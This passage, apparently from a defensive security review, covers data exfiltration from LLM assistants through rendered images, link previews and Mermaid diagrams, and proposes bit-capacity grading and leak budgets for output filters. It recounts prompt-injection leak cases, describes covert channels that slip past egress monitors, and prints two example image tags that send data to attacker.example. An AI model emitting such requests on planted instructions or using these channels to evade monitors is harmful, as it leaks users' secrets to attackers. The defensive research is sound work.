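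| SVG code within the page | The browser, on display | Yes | Active unless a sanitiser removes scripts |
| CSS | The browser, on display, for backgrounds and fonts | No | Automatically fetched |
| HTML preview | The browser, when the preview opens | Yes, if the preview allows scripts | Active |
| Button | The browser or the application's server, after a click | Depends on the action behind it | Link, or active if the click runs code the model wrote |
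| File the assistant writes | Whatever opens the file, possibly much later | Depends on the format | Same as the most dangerous construct inside |

Some of these entries depend on the setting. For example, browsers don't run scripts in an SVG file that a page loads as an image, but they do if the user opens the file directly. HTML previews, which display web pages written by the model, are designed to run such content, and ChatGPT's preview had a flaw.

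Files are easy to overlook because saving them doesn't send a request. *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems* includes a test in which planted text asks a research agent for an image and an "Approve invoice" link, both with placeholders for the user's details in their URLs. The finished report had a separate section with the image and the link, and repeated the demand that they appear there. The test's scoring gives half marks for copying them without filling in the details, since the URLs then contain nothing private. The request is sent when a person or an automated process opens such a report in a program that displays Markdown images. In one of the ReLeak attacks, Microsoft's background processing opened the file.

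The second and third questions don't affect a construct's class, but they matter when comparing constructs within a class. A weather assistant might display one of six icons from the developer's own server, with the model choosing only which one. That icon and an image whose whole address the model wrote are both automatically fetched content, but the icon reveals very little, while the model-written address can contain a password. A construct's capacity, meaning how much information it can carry, depends mainly on how much of the address the model controls.

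### Checking the parsed result

It is tempting to look for risky constructs by searching the model's raw text for patterns. EchoLeak's reference-style links got past Copilot's filter, and there are many more forms that a pattern can miss. Both of these lines can send a request to `attacker.example`, although neither contains the characters `https://`:

```
![chart](https&#58;//attacker.example/48000)
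<img alt="chart" src=//attacker.example/48000>
```

In the first line, `&#58;` is the HTML code for a colon, and standard Markdown software decodes it inside addresses. The second line works where the renderer accepts HTML. Its address leaves out `https:`, so the browser uses the current page's protocol.

Pattern searches also block harmless text. If a user asks how to insert an image in Markdown, a good answer shows an example inside a code block. The renderer displays the example as text without making a request, but a pattern filter would delete the example the user asked for.

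A filter can avoid both errors by running the same parser as the renderer, with the same version and settings, and classifying the resulting elements. After parsing, both lines above are image elements with addresses the filter can read, while the example in the code block is still text. If a second component processes part of the result, the filter has to check that component's output too. This isn't possible when another company runs the last parser, as with Slack. The team then has to rely on what its test server recorded and assume that any form it hasn't tried can cause a request.

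### Link previews in messaging apps

A team that tests its assistant in a browser will not notice requests from a messaging app's preview service, because the messaging company's server sends them and they don't appear in the browser's network log. The developers also didn't write the preview service and may not think of it as part of their product.

PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* tested OpenClaw, an AI agent that people can message through apps such as Telegram. Under Telegram's default settings, a link in an OpenClaw message triggered a preview request as soon as the message arrived. The request sent the link's full address to PromptArmor's test site, and the published log contains a name and an API key, a secret code that gives a program access to a service.

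Users can prevent this by adding `linkPreview: false` to the Telegram section of OpenClaw's configuration file. When PromptArmor repeated the test with this setting, no data reached its site. The link was no longer fetched automatically, so it belonged to the class of links instead of the class of automatically fetched content.

In *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, Willison (2024) passes on Rehberger's advice to set both `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to `false` when posting a message to Slack. Every part of the product that posts to Slack has to do this. If one part, such as a scheduled summary, omits the settings, its messages can still leak data through link previews. Sending all messages through one function that always includes both settings is safer. PromptArmor would like messaging companies to offer preview settings for a whole chat or channel, which would make such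 omissions less likely.

PromptArmor's test site is public, so anyone can test other pairings of agent and app. It shows what data arrived and which preview service sent it, and collects reports of pairings that produced no preview. Testers should use made-up data, since the site records what it receives.

### Images inside Mermaid diagrams

In Markdown, a Mermaid diagram is a code block labeled `mermaid`, so a Markdown parser reports it as code, which is normally inert. But if the application includes Mermaid, Mermaid turns the block into a diagram, and a box in that diagram can contain an external image. The browser, or a code editor built on browser technology, then fetches the image.

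*Takedown* found this in A2, one of the eight coding agents it tested. The researchers planted instructions in an issue, a public report of a problem with a program, and assumed that a developer would ask the agent to retrieve it. A2 could read files outside the developer's project without asking for approval. It read an API key from a settings file in the developer's home folder, then wrote a diagram with the key in an image URL. Drawing the diagram sent the key to the researchers' server. They ran the test in their own private project. Someone else had already reported the flaw to the vendor.

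Rehberger reported the same problem in the code editor Cursor on 30 June 2025. Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE* describes two demonstrations, one that stole API keys and another that stole everything Cursor had remembered about the user. The diagram appears all at once, so the user cannot see the data in the address as the model writes it. Cursor's developers resolved the issue within a week and released the fix in version 1.3 on 29 July.

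MITRE's *Cursor* (2025), a public vulnerability record from October, reports further ways around that fix. Version 1.7 closed them. The record doesn't describe them, so it is hard to say whether the first fix relied on patterns. A filter that checked the finished diagram for outside addresses would at least not depend on knowing every way to put a picture into Mermaid's text. Teams that don't need pictures in diagrams can remove them all from the finished diagram.

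### A log viewer that displayed blocked answers

A copy of a dangerous answer may remain in a log even when an application blocks the answer. PromptArmor found that the log viewer on OpenAI's developer platform displayed such copies as Markdown, including images. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* demonstrates this with a mock version of the tools banks use to check customers' identities. The mock tool combines private customer data with other sources, one of which contains planted instructions from the web.

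The model's answer included a Markdown image with the customer's data in its URL. A second model, acting as a judge, flagged the answer, so the application didn't show it to the user. When a developer later opened the log to investigate, the log viewer rendered the answer as Markdown, the developer's browser requested the image, and the attacker received the customer's passport and financial details.

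Blocking the answer made the leak more likely in one respect, because people tend to review the answers that a filter has flagged. Removing only the image doesn't avoid this problem. PromptArmor shows a reply from Perplexity, an AI search service, that was left oddly empty after a filter stripped out an image. A user might well give such a reply a thumbs-down, and a developer might then open it for review. This is a possible route, not a demonstrated leak from Perplexity's logs.

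The application's filter can't protect the log viewer, because OpenAI stores the original answer before the filter runs. Until OpenAI fixes the viewer, developers should read flagged answers as plain text in another program. PromptArmor found the same problem in several of the platform's preview windows, where developers try out assistants and agents before release, and in a starter application that OpenAI provides for developers to build on. An inventory should therefore include the team's own tools, even if customers never see them.

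PromptArmor reported the flaw on 17 November 2025 through Bugcrowd, which receives such reports for OpenAI. Bugcrowd closed the report as "not applicable" on 4 December. OpenAI had not seen the original report and confirmed the flaw only after PromptArmor published its article. OpenAI reopened the report and said a fix was under way on 22 January 2026, the last date in the article's timeline.

### What OWASP's category covers

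OWASP is a nonprofit whose application security lists many companies use as a baseline. Its list of the ten main risks in applications built on language models includes *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*, which it defines as insufficient checking and cleaning of a model's output before the output goes to other components. The examples include output that an application runs as a system command, inserts into a database query or displays as a web page with a working script. In one scenario, which is close to an image leak, a malicious web page causes a summariser to send private data to an attacker's server, but OWASP doesn't say which construct carries the data.

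The current edition is dated 3 August 2026 (OWASP, 2026). HackerDNA reports that the category now explicitly includes renderers that fetch Markdown images automatically, along with terminals and code editors that act on control codes in the output. The category also fell from fifth place to tenth. HackerDNA's explanation, that developers already know how to fix the problem, may be partly right. Respan's *OWASP LLM Top 10* (2026) says that the ranking combines a community vote, which counts for three quarters, with a record of past incidents. Because the ranking is relative, a lower place doesn't mean that the risk in a particular product has shrunk.

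Published classifications disagree on how to categorize data leaks through images. *Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026) links improper output handling to weaknesses that let output run as code, and places data exfiltration under a different OWASP category, sensitive information disclosure. MITRE's *Cursor's Mermaid Diagram Tool is Vulnerable to an Arbitrary Image Fetch* (2025) classifies the first of Cursor's two Mermaid flaws as server-side request forgery, while the later record classifies the second as exposure of sensitive information. Searching for past cases under a single category will therefore miss some of them.

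OWASP's 2025 advice is also mainly about code. OWASP recommends encoding the output so that the browser shows markup as text, and using a strict CSP against injected scripts. Encoding the whole answer would stop image leaks, but it would also remove every useful picture and link. A CSP that restricts only scripts still lets the browser load images from anywhere. Developers must still decide which images and links an assistant may show, such as whether to allow a product photo from the shop's own server when the model wrote only the product number in the photo's address.

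## Grading constructs by the values they can carry

A filter that applies one rule to everything the model writes into an address must either block a product photo at `https://shop.example/photo?id=381` or let through addresses that contain whole passwords. A graded filter is stricter with constructs that can carry more data, so its author needs a way to measure how much each construct can carry.

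### Counting in bits

A construct's capacity is the most information it can carry, in bits. A yes-or-no value carries one bit, and each further bit doubles the number of possibilities, so b bits can distinguish 2ᵇ secrets. Each secret needs a different request, so a construct that lets the model make k different requests has a capacity of log₂ k bits, the number of doublings from 1 to k. For example, a model that can choose one of six weather icons can convey at most 2.6 bits with that choice.

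This limit holds for any code the attacker invents. *L3M* (Eisenach, George and colleagues, 2026), which describes a system for running AI agents, notes that a choice among 256 options carries at most one byte (8 bits), "whatever was read to make it". The paper adds that the receiver has to know the options independently, because options written with knowledge of the secret carry information themselves. If a model reads a mailbox, writes three image addresses and then picks one, the addresses can contain data from the mailbox, so the limit for a choice among three does not apply. The list has to exist before the model sees private data.

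A model that makes n independent choices with k options each can produce kⁿ combinations, which can carry log₂ kⁿ = n log₂ k bits, so the capacities of independent choices add. Free text is a series of such choices, one per character. If a filter permits 64 different characters, each character of text can carry 6 bits, and 100 characters can carry 600 bits. Without a length limit, the capacity of free text is unbounded.

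Capacity is a maximum, and a real attack may achieve less because models make mistakes and requests get lost. A filter should still use the maximum, since the attacker chooses the encoding. Capacity also doesn't measure harm, since a single bit can reveal whether a company is about to be sold.

### A scale for the parts of an address

The table grades the part of an address that the model controls. The grades apply when the host is on the allowlist and the developer has fixed the rest of the address.

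| What the model controls | Example | Capacity | Default treatment |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing | `/logo.png` | 0 bits | Load |
| Yes or no | `?dark=1` | 1 bit | Load and count the bit |
| One item from a list | One of 500 product numbers | 9.0 bits | Load if the value is on the list, and count the bits |
| Bounded number | A picture width from 1 to 2,000 | 11.0 bits | Cut down to a few permitted values if possible, then load and count |
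| Unbounded number | Any string of digits | 3.3 bits per digit, no total limit | Treat as free text |
| Free text | A search phrase | No fixed limit | Do not load automatically |

Users often lose nothing when a number is restricted to a few values. A chat window rarely needs 2,000 picture widths, and permitting only four reduces the data a width can carry from 11 bits to 2.

When an address can carry free text, the filter can show it as plain text or check whether that exact address was already public before the conversation. OpenAI uses the check, and if an address fails, it has the agent try another site or warns the user. The check reduces free text to a choice from a very long list of public addresses. How much data can still leak depends on how many of those addresses lead to servers whose logs the attacker can read.

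The filter's author has to count every distinct request as a separate option, even when several mean the same thing. The shop's server may return the same photo for `381`, `0381` and `00381`, but its log records three different requests. If an address has five parameters and the server accepts them in any order, the order alone can carry 6.9 bits. The simplest remedy is for the model to output only the product number. Ordinary code then looks up the number and builds the address in one fixed form.

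### Spelling out a password with 36 addresses

Suppose an attacker has prepared 36 fixed addresses, as in CamoLeak, one for each letter A to Z and digit 0 to 9, and the filter has approved all of them. Each request goes to one of the 36, so it carries up to log₂ 36, or about 5.17 bits. A random 16-character secret made of these letters and digits contains 16 times as much, about 82.7 bits, so the model can spell it out in 16 requests.

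Embrace The Red points out that a larger website or blog probably already has 36 publicly indexed addresses, and that an attacker could extend the scheme to thousands. With 4,096 addresses, each request carries 12 bits, so the same secret takes seven requests. The gain is modest for 114 times as many addresses because doubling the list adds only one bit per request. Sending the secret in a single request would take about 8 × 10²⁴ addresses.

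Limiting the number of requests is therefore much more effective than shortening the list. If the filter shortened the attacker's list from 4,096 addresses to 36, the attacker would need 16 requests instead of seven. If it allowed only three requests to the attacker's server, those requests could carry at most 36 of the 82.7 bits, even with the full list.

### A login code is also a number

A rule that limits model-written values to numbers can still leak a login code. Many services confirm a login with a short numeric code, and NIST's *Authenticator and Verifier Requirements*, part of the US government's standard for digital identity, sets a minimum of six digits for randomly generated codes sent to a user's device. A six-digit code is one of a million possibilities, or about 19.9 bits. If the code is 493027, an address ending in `?size=493027` satisfies the rule and contains the entire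 code.

NIST also requires such a login to be completed within ten minutes, but a code leaked through an image could still be valid because images load within seconds. The standard prohibits services from emailing these codes, but many do, so an email assistant will come across them.

A range check blocks this address if the largest permitted size is, say, 60. For decimals, the filter also has to limit the number of digits, because a value between 0 and 1 can still contain the whole code, as in `0.493027`, and more decimal places could carry more data.

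Numbers without a limit are no safer than text, because anyone can convert text into digits. The 16-character secret from the previous example fits in a 25-digit number.

### Instructions coming in and secrets going out

Much of the published work on restricting value types aims to stop planted instructions, not leaks. In *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*, Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025) split an agent into a quarantined part, which reads untrusted text, and a privileged part, which decides what to do. The quarantined part may pass on only whole numbers, decimals, yes-or-no values and items from a developer-vetted list. In their shopping agent, it turns each customer review into two scores, for how strongly the review supports the product and how relevant it is. Instructions planted in a review can distort these scores, but they can't reach the privileged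 part and direct it to buy something else.

An integer is harmless here because the receiver is a model, and the integer could do harm only if the model read it as a command. Jacob and colleagues also cap the length of lists, since a long list of numbers could be decoded into text.

An attacker who receives a value from the application knows in advance what to look for, so any value that can vary can carry information, even if it doesn't resemble language. An attacker can't use the number 493027 to give a planner instructions, but if a request carries it to the attacker's server, it may be all they need to log in. The sales manager's confidential quote of 48,000 euros was also a plain integer.

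Developers also vet lists for a different reason in each direction. They check that no item in a list of incoming values reads like an instruction, and the list can be as long as the task requires. Length matters for a list of outgoing values, because the list can leak data even if every item is harmless, as the 36 addresses show. A team that already restricts incoming values therefore can't assume that the same types are safe in a web address.

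### Channels that separate grades miss

A filter that grades each address separately can miss information in how the model combines them. Suppose an assistant always ends its answer with the same eight pictures. Each address is fixed, so it gets a grade of 0 bits. But if the model chooses the order of the pictures, there are 40,320 possibilities, and the order in which the requests arrive can carry up to 15.3 bits.

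Repetition also carries information. A model that can display one fixed image between 0 and 15 times has 16 options, or 4 bits, if each display causes a new request. Embrace The Red notes that browser caching and out-of-order requests hinder the attacker. As further defenses, it suggests caching responses for a few minutes or preventing an agent from visiting the same full URL twice in a session.

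Blocking repeats helps more when the attacker can't see the order of the requests. With 36 addresses and the order visible, an attacker who adapts the code needs 18 requests instead of 16 to send the 16-character secret, and can send at most about 140 bits per session before the addresses run out. If the order is hidden too, the log shows only which of the 36 addresses the browser requested, and the limit falls to 36 bits. That is too few for the 16-character secret but enough for a login code.

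There are other choices that no single field reveals:

- **Whether a request occurs:** A fixed picture that appears only if the user's salary is above a certain amount carries one bit. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* makes a similar allowance.
- **Which construct the model uses:** If the attacker's server can distinguish four constructs, such as an image and a link preview, the choice carries 2 bits.
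- **Timing:** If images load while the answer is still arriving, as in SearchLeak, the model can write a short or a long paragraph between two of them. The attacker can measure the gap, though network delays blur it.
- **Spacing and invisible characters:** Text can contain extra spaces or characters with no visible shape, which reach outsiders in a public comment or inside an address.

*Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) bounds the leak from an agent that may send only messages from a fixed set of D messages. Each message leaks at most log₂(D + 1) bits, where the added 1 presumably stands for a message outside the set. With a single permitted message, the bound is one bit. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) ranks value types by capacity, but its guarantee explicitly excludes the order of tool calls, timing and the length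 of network packets.

### A monitor for hidden channels

Security researchers call hidden signals like these covert channels. *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (Metere, 2026) describes a program that looks for them in an agent's outgoing messages. The paper assumes that an attacker already controls what the agent tries to send and knows how the program works.

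All outgoing text passes through one monitor, which applies ten techniques. Some estimate how much hidden information a message might contain, for example by looking for long random-looking strings. Others rewrite the text by stripping invisible characters, replacing look-alike letters from other alphabets, putting data fields into a standard order, or swapping synonyms for one standard word. The rest control when and how often the agent may send messages. The monitor also tracks how much of its allowance each destination has used, and can delay or cancel suspicious messages once the allowance runs out.

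For each channel, Metere wrote one program that hid random bits in a harmless message and another that tried to recover them after the monitor had processed the message. He ran 20 trials for each combination of channel and setting and calculated how much of the information survived. By default, the monitor enforces only the techniques that he considers harmless to normal text and logs what the others detect.

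| Where the data was hidden | Capacity removed by default | Capacity removed with everything enforced |
|---|---|---|
| Invisible characters, text-direction marks, look-alike letters, order of data fields | 100% | 100% |
| Number of spaces, repeated punctuation, synonyms, encoded blocks of data | 0% | 100% |
| Time between messages | Not reported | 100% |
| Mean over the text benchmark | 60.2% | 100% |

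By default, the monitor flagged every trial in the second row but still let the data out. Rounding the send times left about a fifth of the timing channel's capacity. Only sending at fixed intervals removed all of it, but this makes the agent slower to respond.

Metere also found that four images in a freely chosen order carry about 4.6 bits, and that sorting them by a code computed from their content reduced this to zero. A filter with an image proxy could similarly wait for the complete answer, drop duplicates and fetch the images in a fixed order. The user would still see them in the order the model chose. The data carried by brightness was harder to remove, because making all images equally bright would ruin them. Rounding brightness to eight levels leaves 3 bits per image.

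The 100 per cent figures apply only to the encodings that Metere tested, and he acknowledges that whether the agent sends anything always conveys one bit. None of his encoders spelled out data through a choice of web addresses, the method used in CamoLeak, so his results offer little evidence about that attack. The text monitor also doesn't cover structured blocks such as buttons. Metere works for Enclawed, which offers the monitor as part of its product. The paper leaves some points unresolved. For example, an illustration shows the default clean-up removing extra spaces, but the channel that hides data in extra spaces kept its full capacity in the test.

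Metere says the default setting guarantees zero false positives, but he did not measure how often the monitor damages or blocks harmless messages. It probably damages some, because it strips an invisible character used in Persian spelling, and some emoji also depend on invisible characters.

### Budgets per answer and per session

The filter has to add up the bits it lets through and stop at a fixed total, because a secret can be split across constructs. If the filter only limits each construct to 10 bits, two constructs can carry a login code and nine can carry the 16-character secret.

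Google built such a budget into Chrome. A website could give the browser a list of addresses, and code with access to data about the user from several sites picked one to display. According to Google's *Select URL overview*, a choice among eight addresses used log₂ 8, or 3 bits. Each site could use up to 6 bits per page load and 12 bits per day. The daily budget counted a choice only if the displayed content took the user to a new page. When a site had too little left for the day, the browser returned the first address on the list. A chat application could similarly show a standard picture instead of an error.

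Google's rules didn't count reusing a saved choice on the same page, because it revealed nothing new. A chat filter shouldn't copy this rule for repeated images, because the model decides whether to repeat them. The filter should skip counting a repeat only if it causes no new request.

Google began retiring the feature in Chrome 144, for stated reasons that don't concern the arithmetic. Barnes (2025) explains in *Intent To Deprecate and Remove* that Chrome is keeping third-party cookies, which serve the same purposes, and that other browsers showed no interest in the feature.

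*Answer-Only Disclosure* (2026) tested a budget on the text of answers, using a secret code planted in private documents. The system revealed the code in 46 of 48 cases without a budget, and in none with a budget of 16 nats (about 23 bits) per answer. This is encouraging but no guarantee, because 23 bits are in principle enough for a six-digit code. The median answer used only 10 nats, but step-by-step solutions to maths problems averaged 52 to 72, so a budget that suits short answers may be too tight for long ones.

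A reasonable way to set the budget is to start from the smallest secret that needs protection. If 16 of a login code's 19.9 bits leak, about 15 possible codes remain, and an attacker could try them all. If 10 bits leak, nearly 1,000 remain. NIST requires services to limit failed attempts, and five guesses among those codes would give the attacker about a 1 in 200 chance of success.

A ten-bit budget is small for a shopping assistant. Three photos from a catalogue of 500 products can carry 27 bits, so the budget would allow only one. The team can avoid this by applying the budget only to hosts that an attacker might control or observe. Its own server can be exempt if outsiders can't read the server's logs and the server doesn't forward requests. EchoLeak shows why the team needs to check for forwarding.

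A limit per answer is too weak on its own, because the model can leak more data in its next answer. The filter also needs a limit for the whole session. Eisenach and colleagues propose adding up the full length of every outgoing request over an agent's whole run, since any byte could hide part of a secret. They have not yet implemented this design.

Even a session budget resets when the user opens a new chat, but a planted email stays in the mailbox, so the attack can continue. At 10 bits per session and one session a day, the whole 16-character secret would leak in nine days. A login code would expire before the second session, but a password or API key may stay valid for months. To protect such secrets, the filter needs a running total for each user and destination that does not reset with the conversation.

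## Whether grading reduces false blocks without new leaks

A graded filter lets through some constructs that a block-everything filter removes, so it will cause fewer false blocks. It will also let some information out, unless the model cannot influence what those constructs contain. A team needs to know how many false blocks disappear and how much an attacker gains. None of the five studies closest to this question directly tests a graded filter on displayed answers. Three of them describe agents that restrict the types of values passed between their parts. Those agents still completed many of their tasks, which is encouraging about false blocks. The three studies provide much less evidence about leaks, because nearly all the attacks tried to insert instructions, whereas a filter has to stop secrets from getting out.

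### What counts as a new leak

A useful assistant discloses some information on purpose. When it displays a product photo, the photo's host learns which product the user is looking at. When it answers a stranger's meeting request, the stranger learns when the user is free. Nearly every assistant would fail under a definition that counted these disclosures as failures.

*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) defines an agent's security by comparing it with a reference agent. The reference agent carries out the same plan under the same monitor, which is the code that permits or denies each action, but its model never obeys instructions in untrusted content. An agent is relatively secure if every leak it has also occurs in the reference agent.

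Here, an agent leaks a pair of secrets if the attacker sees something different in two runs where the attacker supplies the same content and only the user's private data differs. The reference agent must also leak every pair that the agent leaks, though possibly in response to different content from the attacker.

In one of Dongol's examples, Alice lets her assistant send her calendar to anyone who asks for a meeting. An attacker's email tells the assistant to send the calendar, and it obeys. This is not a new leak, because the attacker could have got the calendar with a genuine meeting request. If the email also asks for a password reset code and the assistant sends it, the assistant is not relatively secure, because no email would make the reference agent send the code.

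To apply the definition to a filter, we must treat every web request that an answer causes as something the attacker may see. Dongol's theorems don't cover this case directly, because they assume that displaying a reply causes no request visible to the attacker, such as one for an image. Suppose a graded filter lets a shopping assistant choose one of 64 photos. The choice normally depends on the user's question, but planted instructions can make it depend on a login code in the user's mailbox. Two different codes can then lead to different photos, while the reference agent would show the same photo for both. This is a new leak, even though every address is on the list and the choice carries only 6 bits.

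By this standard, a graded filter generally fails if it lets a misled model make a choice that the attacker can observe. It can pass if something else makes the choice, such as ordinary code that picks the photo from the user's own words before the assistant reads anything else. A team that grades constructs should therefore promise "at most 8 bits per session" rather than "no new leaks".

Blocking a request can itself leak information. In another of Dongol's examples, an injection triggers a request to a permitted address if a secret bit is 0 and to a forbidden address if it is 1. The monitor stops the forbidden request, so the attacker learns the bit from whether a request arrives. One of Dongol's attacker models misses this leak because it compares only runs in which the attacker receives the same number of messages. A stricter model that also tracks when each step happens detects it.

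The definition doesn't measure how many bits leak either. If the reference agent accepts one guess at a secret and replies whether it is right, an agent that sends the entire secret is still relatively secure, because for any two secrets there is a guess that tells them apart. Dongol's stronger version, uniform relative security, closes this gap by letting the reference agent's input depend on what the attacker sent but not on the secret. A filter that meets the basic definition still needs a limit on how many bits it can leak.

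False blocks also need to be measured separately. Dongol points out that a monitor that denies every call is trivially secure, because the reference agent runs under the same monitor and can't make any calls either.

Dongol proves that one simple rule is relatively secure. As soon as the agent reads untrusted content, the monitor permanently withdraws every tool that an injection could call. The proof assumes that each injection causes a single call and that the model follows injections on a schedule fixed in advance. A chat application could apply a similar rule by loading no outside images for the rest of a session once the assistant has read an outside document. For an assistant that rarely reads such documents, this might cause fewer false blocks than grading. An email assistant reads strangers' messages in almost every session, so the rule would come close to blocking everything.

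The effect of grading also depends on the filter it replaces. Every bit it lets through is a new leak if the old filter blocked everything, but grading removes leaks if it replaces an allowlist of hosts that accepts any path or query. In EchoLeak, the attacker's address was in the query of a request to an allowed Teams host, so a filter that refused free text in that field would have blocked the image. The same rule would have stopped ForcedLeak, where the image address contained customers' details. It would not have stopped CamoLeak, where every address was fixed in advance and only a limit on the number of images would have helped.

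### Three agents that restrict value types

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, has the design closest to a graded filter. It labels each piece of data with how far the agent can trust it and who may read it. When a tool returns untrusted data, FIDES stores the data in a variable and shows only the variable's name to the planner, the part of the agent that decides what to do next. A second model without tools can read the variable and answer a question about it. The planner specifies the answer's type, which is included in the answer's label. FIDES ranks yes-or-no values below items from a fixed list, and both below free text, so a policy can relax its rules for values that carry less information.

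For example, a user might ask the agent to read three emails and, if one requests a meeting, add it to the calendar. A rule against acting on untrusted data would block the calendar entry. With FIDES, the planner can use the second model to check whether any email requests a meeting, and receive only a yes or no. The policy can then permit the entry, because one bit is unlikely to contain an instruction and the meeting's details stay in a variable. Costa and colleagues note that low-capacity values are also less useful for exfiltrating data.

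However, the version of FIDES they tested doesn't force answers into a type, because most tasks in AgentDojo, the benchmark they used, don't need it. Jacob and colleagues also observe that the FIDES paper mentions typed answers but doesn't develop or evaluate them. The results therefore cover only the labels and variables.

AgentDojo has 97 user tasks and 36 attacker goals in simulated office, travel, banking and Slack environments. With GPT-4o as the model, an unprotected agent carried out 152 planted instructions. FIDES carried out 21 with its rules switched off. With the rules on, AgentDojo's automatic scoring counted three successes, but Costa and colleagues inspected them and found that none was real.

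The rules also stopped harmless work. With o1, a stronger model, FIDES completed an average of 78 per cent of tasks without the rules and 61 per cent with them. The loss was 23 percentage points in banking and 25 in Slack, compared with 13 in the office environment and 7 in travel. The agent has to look at data before it can choose its next step in more than 40 per cent of banking and Slack tasks, but in at most 10 per cent of tasks in the other two environments. Typed answers are meant for such tasks, so grading might have recovered some of them.

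FIDES blocked every outgoing message that contained a link from an untrusted source, to prevent leaks through web requests. Relaxing this rule for links that carry few bits, and then measuring both false blocks and leaks, would have come close to the missing test of grading.

Jacob and colleagues tested typed values in their type-directed privilege separation, which separates a quarantined part from a privileged part. Planted instructions told their shopping agent to abandon a product and their bug-fixing agent to create an unwanted file, so the tests covered incoming instructions rather than outgoing data. The defence stopped every attack on both agents. The shopping agent performed as well with the defence as without it, but the bug-fixing agent solved only 45 per cent of its tasks, down from 68 per cent. The quarantined part could pass on the type of bug and the suspicious lines of code,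 but not the reporter's explanation. Jacob and colleagues attribute the drop to the importance of such explanations in real bug reports.

Of their three agents, only the calendar agent holds secret data. It negotiates a meeting time by email, and a malicious correspondent asks it for all the user's calendar entries. The researchers added the marker `SCRTINFO` to every entry's description and counted an attack as successful if the marker appeared in an outgoing email. The unprotected agent leaked the marker in 63 per cent of email threads, and the protected agent leaked it in none.

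This shows that the protected agent didn't copy descriptions into its emails, but the emails could still have revealed encoded data, which a search for a fixed marker can't detect. Each calendar covered seven days of nine one-hour slots, so a single proposed time can carry up to 6 bits. An attacker would have found this hard to exploit here, because the part of the agent that chose the times never read the attacker's text. In a chat assistant, the same model usually reads the attacker's text and chooses the output, so a filter on that output has to assume that planted instructions control the choice.

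*Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* (Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues, 2026) applies typed answers to agents that operate websites. Its system replaces reviews, comments and other outside text with labelled placeholders before the agent sees the page. To learn about a hidden element, the agent asks a separate model and specifies the type of answer. A number needs a minimum and a maximum, a list may have at most ten options, and the agent may ask about each element only five times per task. The separate model can return free text only if the user approves it.

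These limits resemble those of a graded filter, but they don't set a bit budget. Five choices among ten options each can carry 16.6 bits, and numbers can carry more because the agent sets their range. A range up to 999,999 can hold an entire login code. This is harmless in their design because the number goes to the agent, not to an attacker.

Nikolić and colleagues tested incoming instructions by planting strengthened attacks in GitLab, a website for managing software projects. The attacks succeeded 17 per cent of the time against an unprotected agent and never against the masked one. When the researchers wrongly marked one untrusted element as trusted, the masked agent's rate rose to 6 per cent. They also examined how an attacker could exploit answers of the right type but with the wrong content. If the separate model wrongly answers "yes" when asked whether a project is the one the user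 named, the agent may invite a colleague to the attacker's project instead. Restricting the type of answer therefore doesn't ensure that an action has the right destination.

Masking caused few false blocks. In 100 tasks on ten purpose-built websites, the agents completed about as many with masking as without it, at 1.05 to 1.84 times the cost. On GitLab, the agents gave up on four of 41 kinds of task, such as naming the person who had contributed most to a project. All four needed free text, and the agents recovered their full success rate once users could approve that text. Approval works less well for outgoing data, because a user who sees `size=47` in an address can't tell whether it encodes part of a password.

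The table compares each agent with and without its defence. The FIDES figures are for GPT-4o, and the FIDES task rate is an average over the four environments.

| Test | What the attacks tried to do | Successful attacks | Tasks completed without an attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| FIDES | Get instructions in (typed answers not tested) | 152 → 0 | 84% → 50% |
| Type-directed separation, shopping | Get instructions in | 31.7% → 0% | 21.8% → 22.4% |
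| Type-directed separation, calendar | Get a marked secret out | 63.0% → 0% | 90.0% → 91.0% |
| Type-directed separation, bug fixing | Get instructions in | 98.9% → 0% | 68.3% → 45.0% |
| Untrusted Content Masking, GitLab attacks | Get instructions in | 17% → 0% | 100% → 100% |

The last column is the most useful for a filter's author. Shopping, scheduling and most website tasks worked without free text from untrusted sources, but tasks that depended on someone's explanation did worse. The pattern is probably similar for displayed answers, where product photos and charts would still work but search links would not. The zeros for attacks don't carry over in the same way, because a number that is useless as an instruction may still be the secret an attacker wants.

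### Labels that spread too widely

Instead of grading constructs by type, a filter could track where data came from and block only constructs that contain private data. The usual objection is that privacy labels spread too widely. Once an agent has read a confidential email, a cautious tracker treats everything it writes afterwards as confidential, including a link to a public train timetable. Costa and colleagues acknowledge that such tracking may be overly cautious. When they added it to a basic agent with GPT-4o, the share of Slack tasks completed fell from 93 to 20 per cent. FIDES, which hides data in variables partly to slow this spread, completed 48 per cent.

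Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, compared FIDES with their own tool, NeuroTaint, which looks for evidence that outside content influenced an agent's later action. NeuroTaint first searches for copied or paraphrased text. If it finds none, it asks a model whether the agent would have done the same without that content. The researchers built 400 scenarios across 20 agent frameworks. In half the scenarios, outside content reached or influenced a sensitive action.

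| | FIDES | NeuroTaint |
|---|---|---|
| False alarms in 200 harmless scenarios | 106 | 16 |
| Missed flows in 200 scenarios with a real flow | 92 | 13 |

FIDES's false alarms correspond to a false block rate of 53 per cent. Most came from scenarios in which the agent read from an outside source and later used a sensitive tool, but no relevant content passed between the two. In the 140 scenarios of this kind, FIDES raised 94 false alarms and NeuroTaint raised one. But NeuroTaint raised false alarms in all 14 cases where the output merely covered the same topic as the source.

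These results support the objection to simple tracking, but they aren't a fair test of graded labels. The FIDES baseline treated a path from source to action as strong evidence of a flow, and the comparison didn't use the ranking by capacity. The baseline also flagged nothing in four of the 20 frameworks, which accounted for 40 of its 92 misses. That looks more like a problem connecting FIDES to those frameworks than a weakness of its method. Cai and colleagues also designed the benchmark around the kinds of flow that NeuroTaint looks for.

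NeuroTaint can't replace a filter, because it blocks nothing and examines an agent's records only after the run, when the browser has already loaded any image in the answer. Even a version that ran before display would have to recognise each data flow, and most of NeuroTaint's 13 misses involved content that the agent had paraphrased or stored and retrieved later. An attacker who encodes a login code as a series of product numbers leaves no similar text to find, but a capacity limit still applies because it doesn't depend on recognising the encoding.

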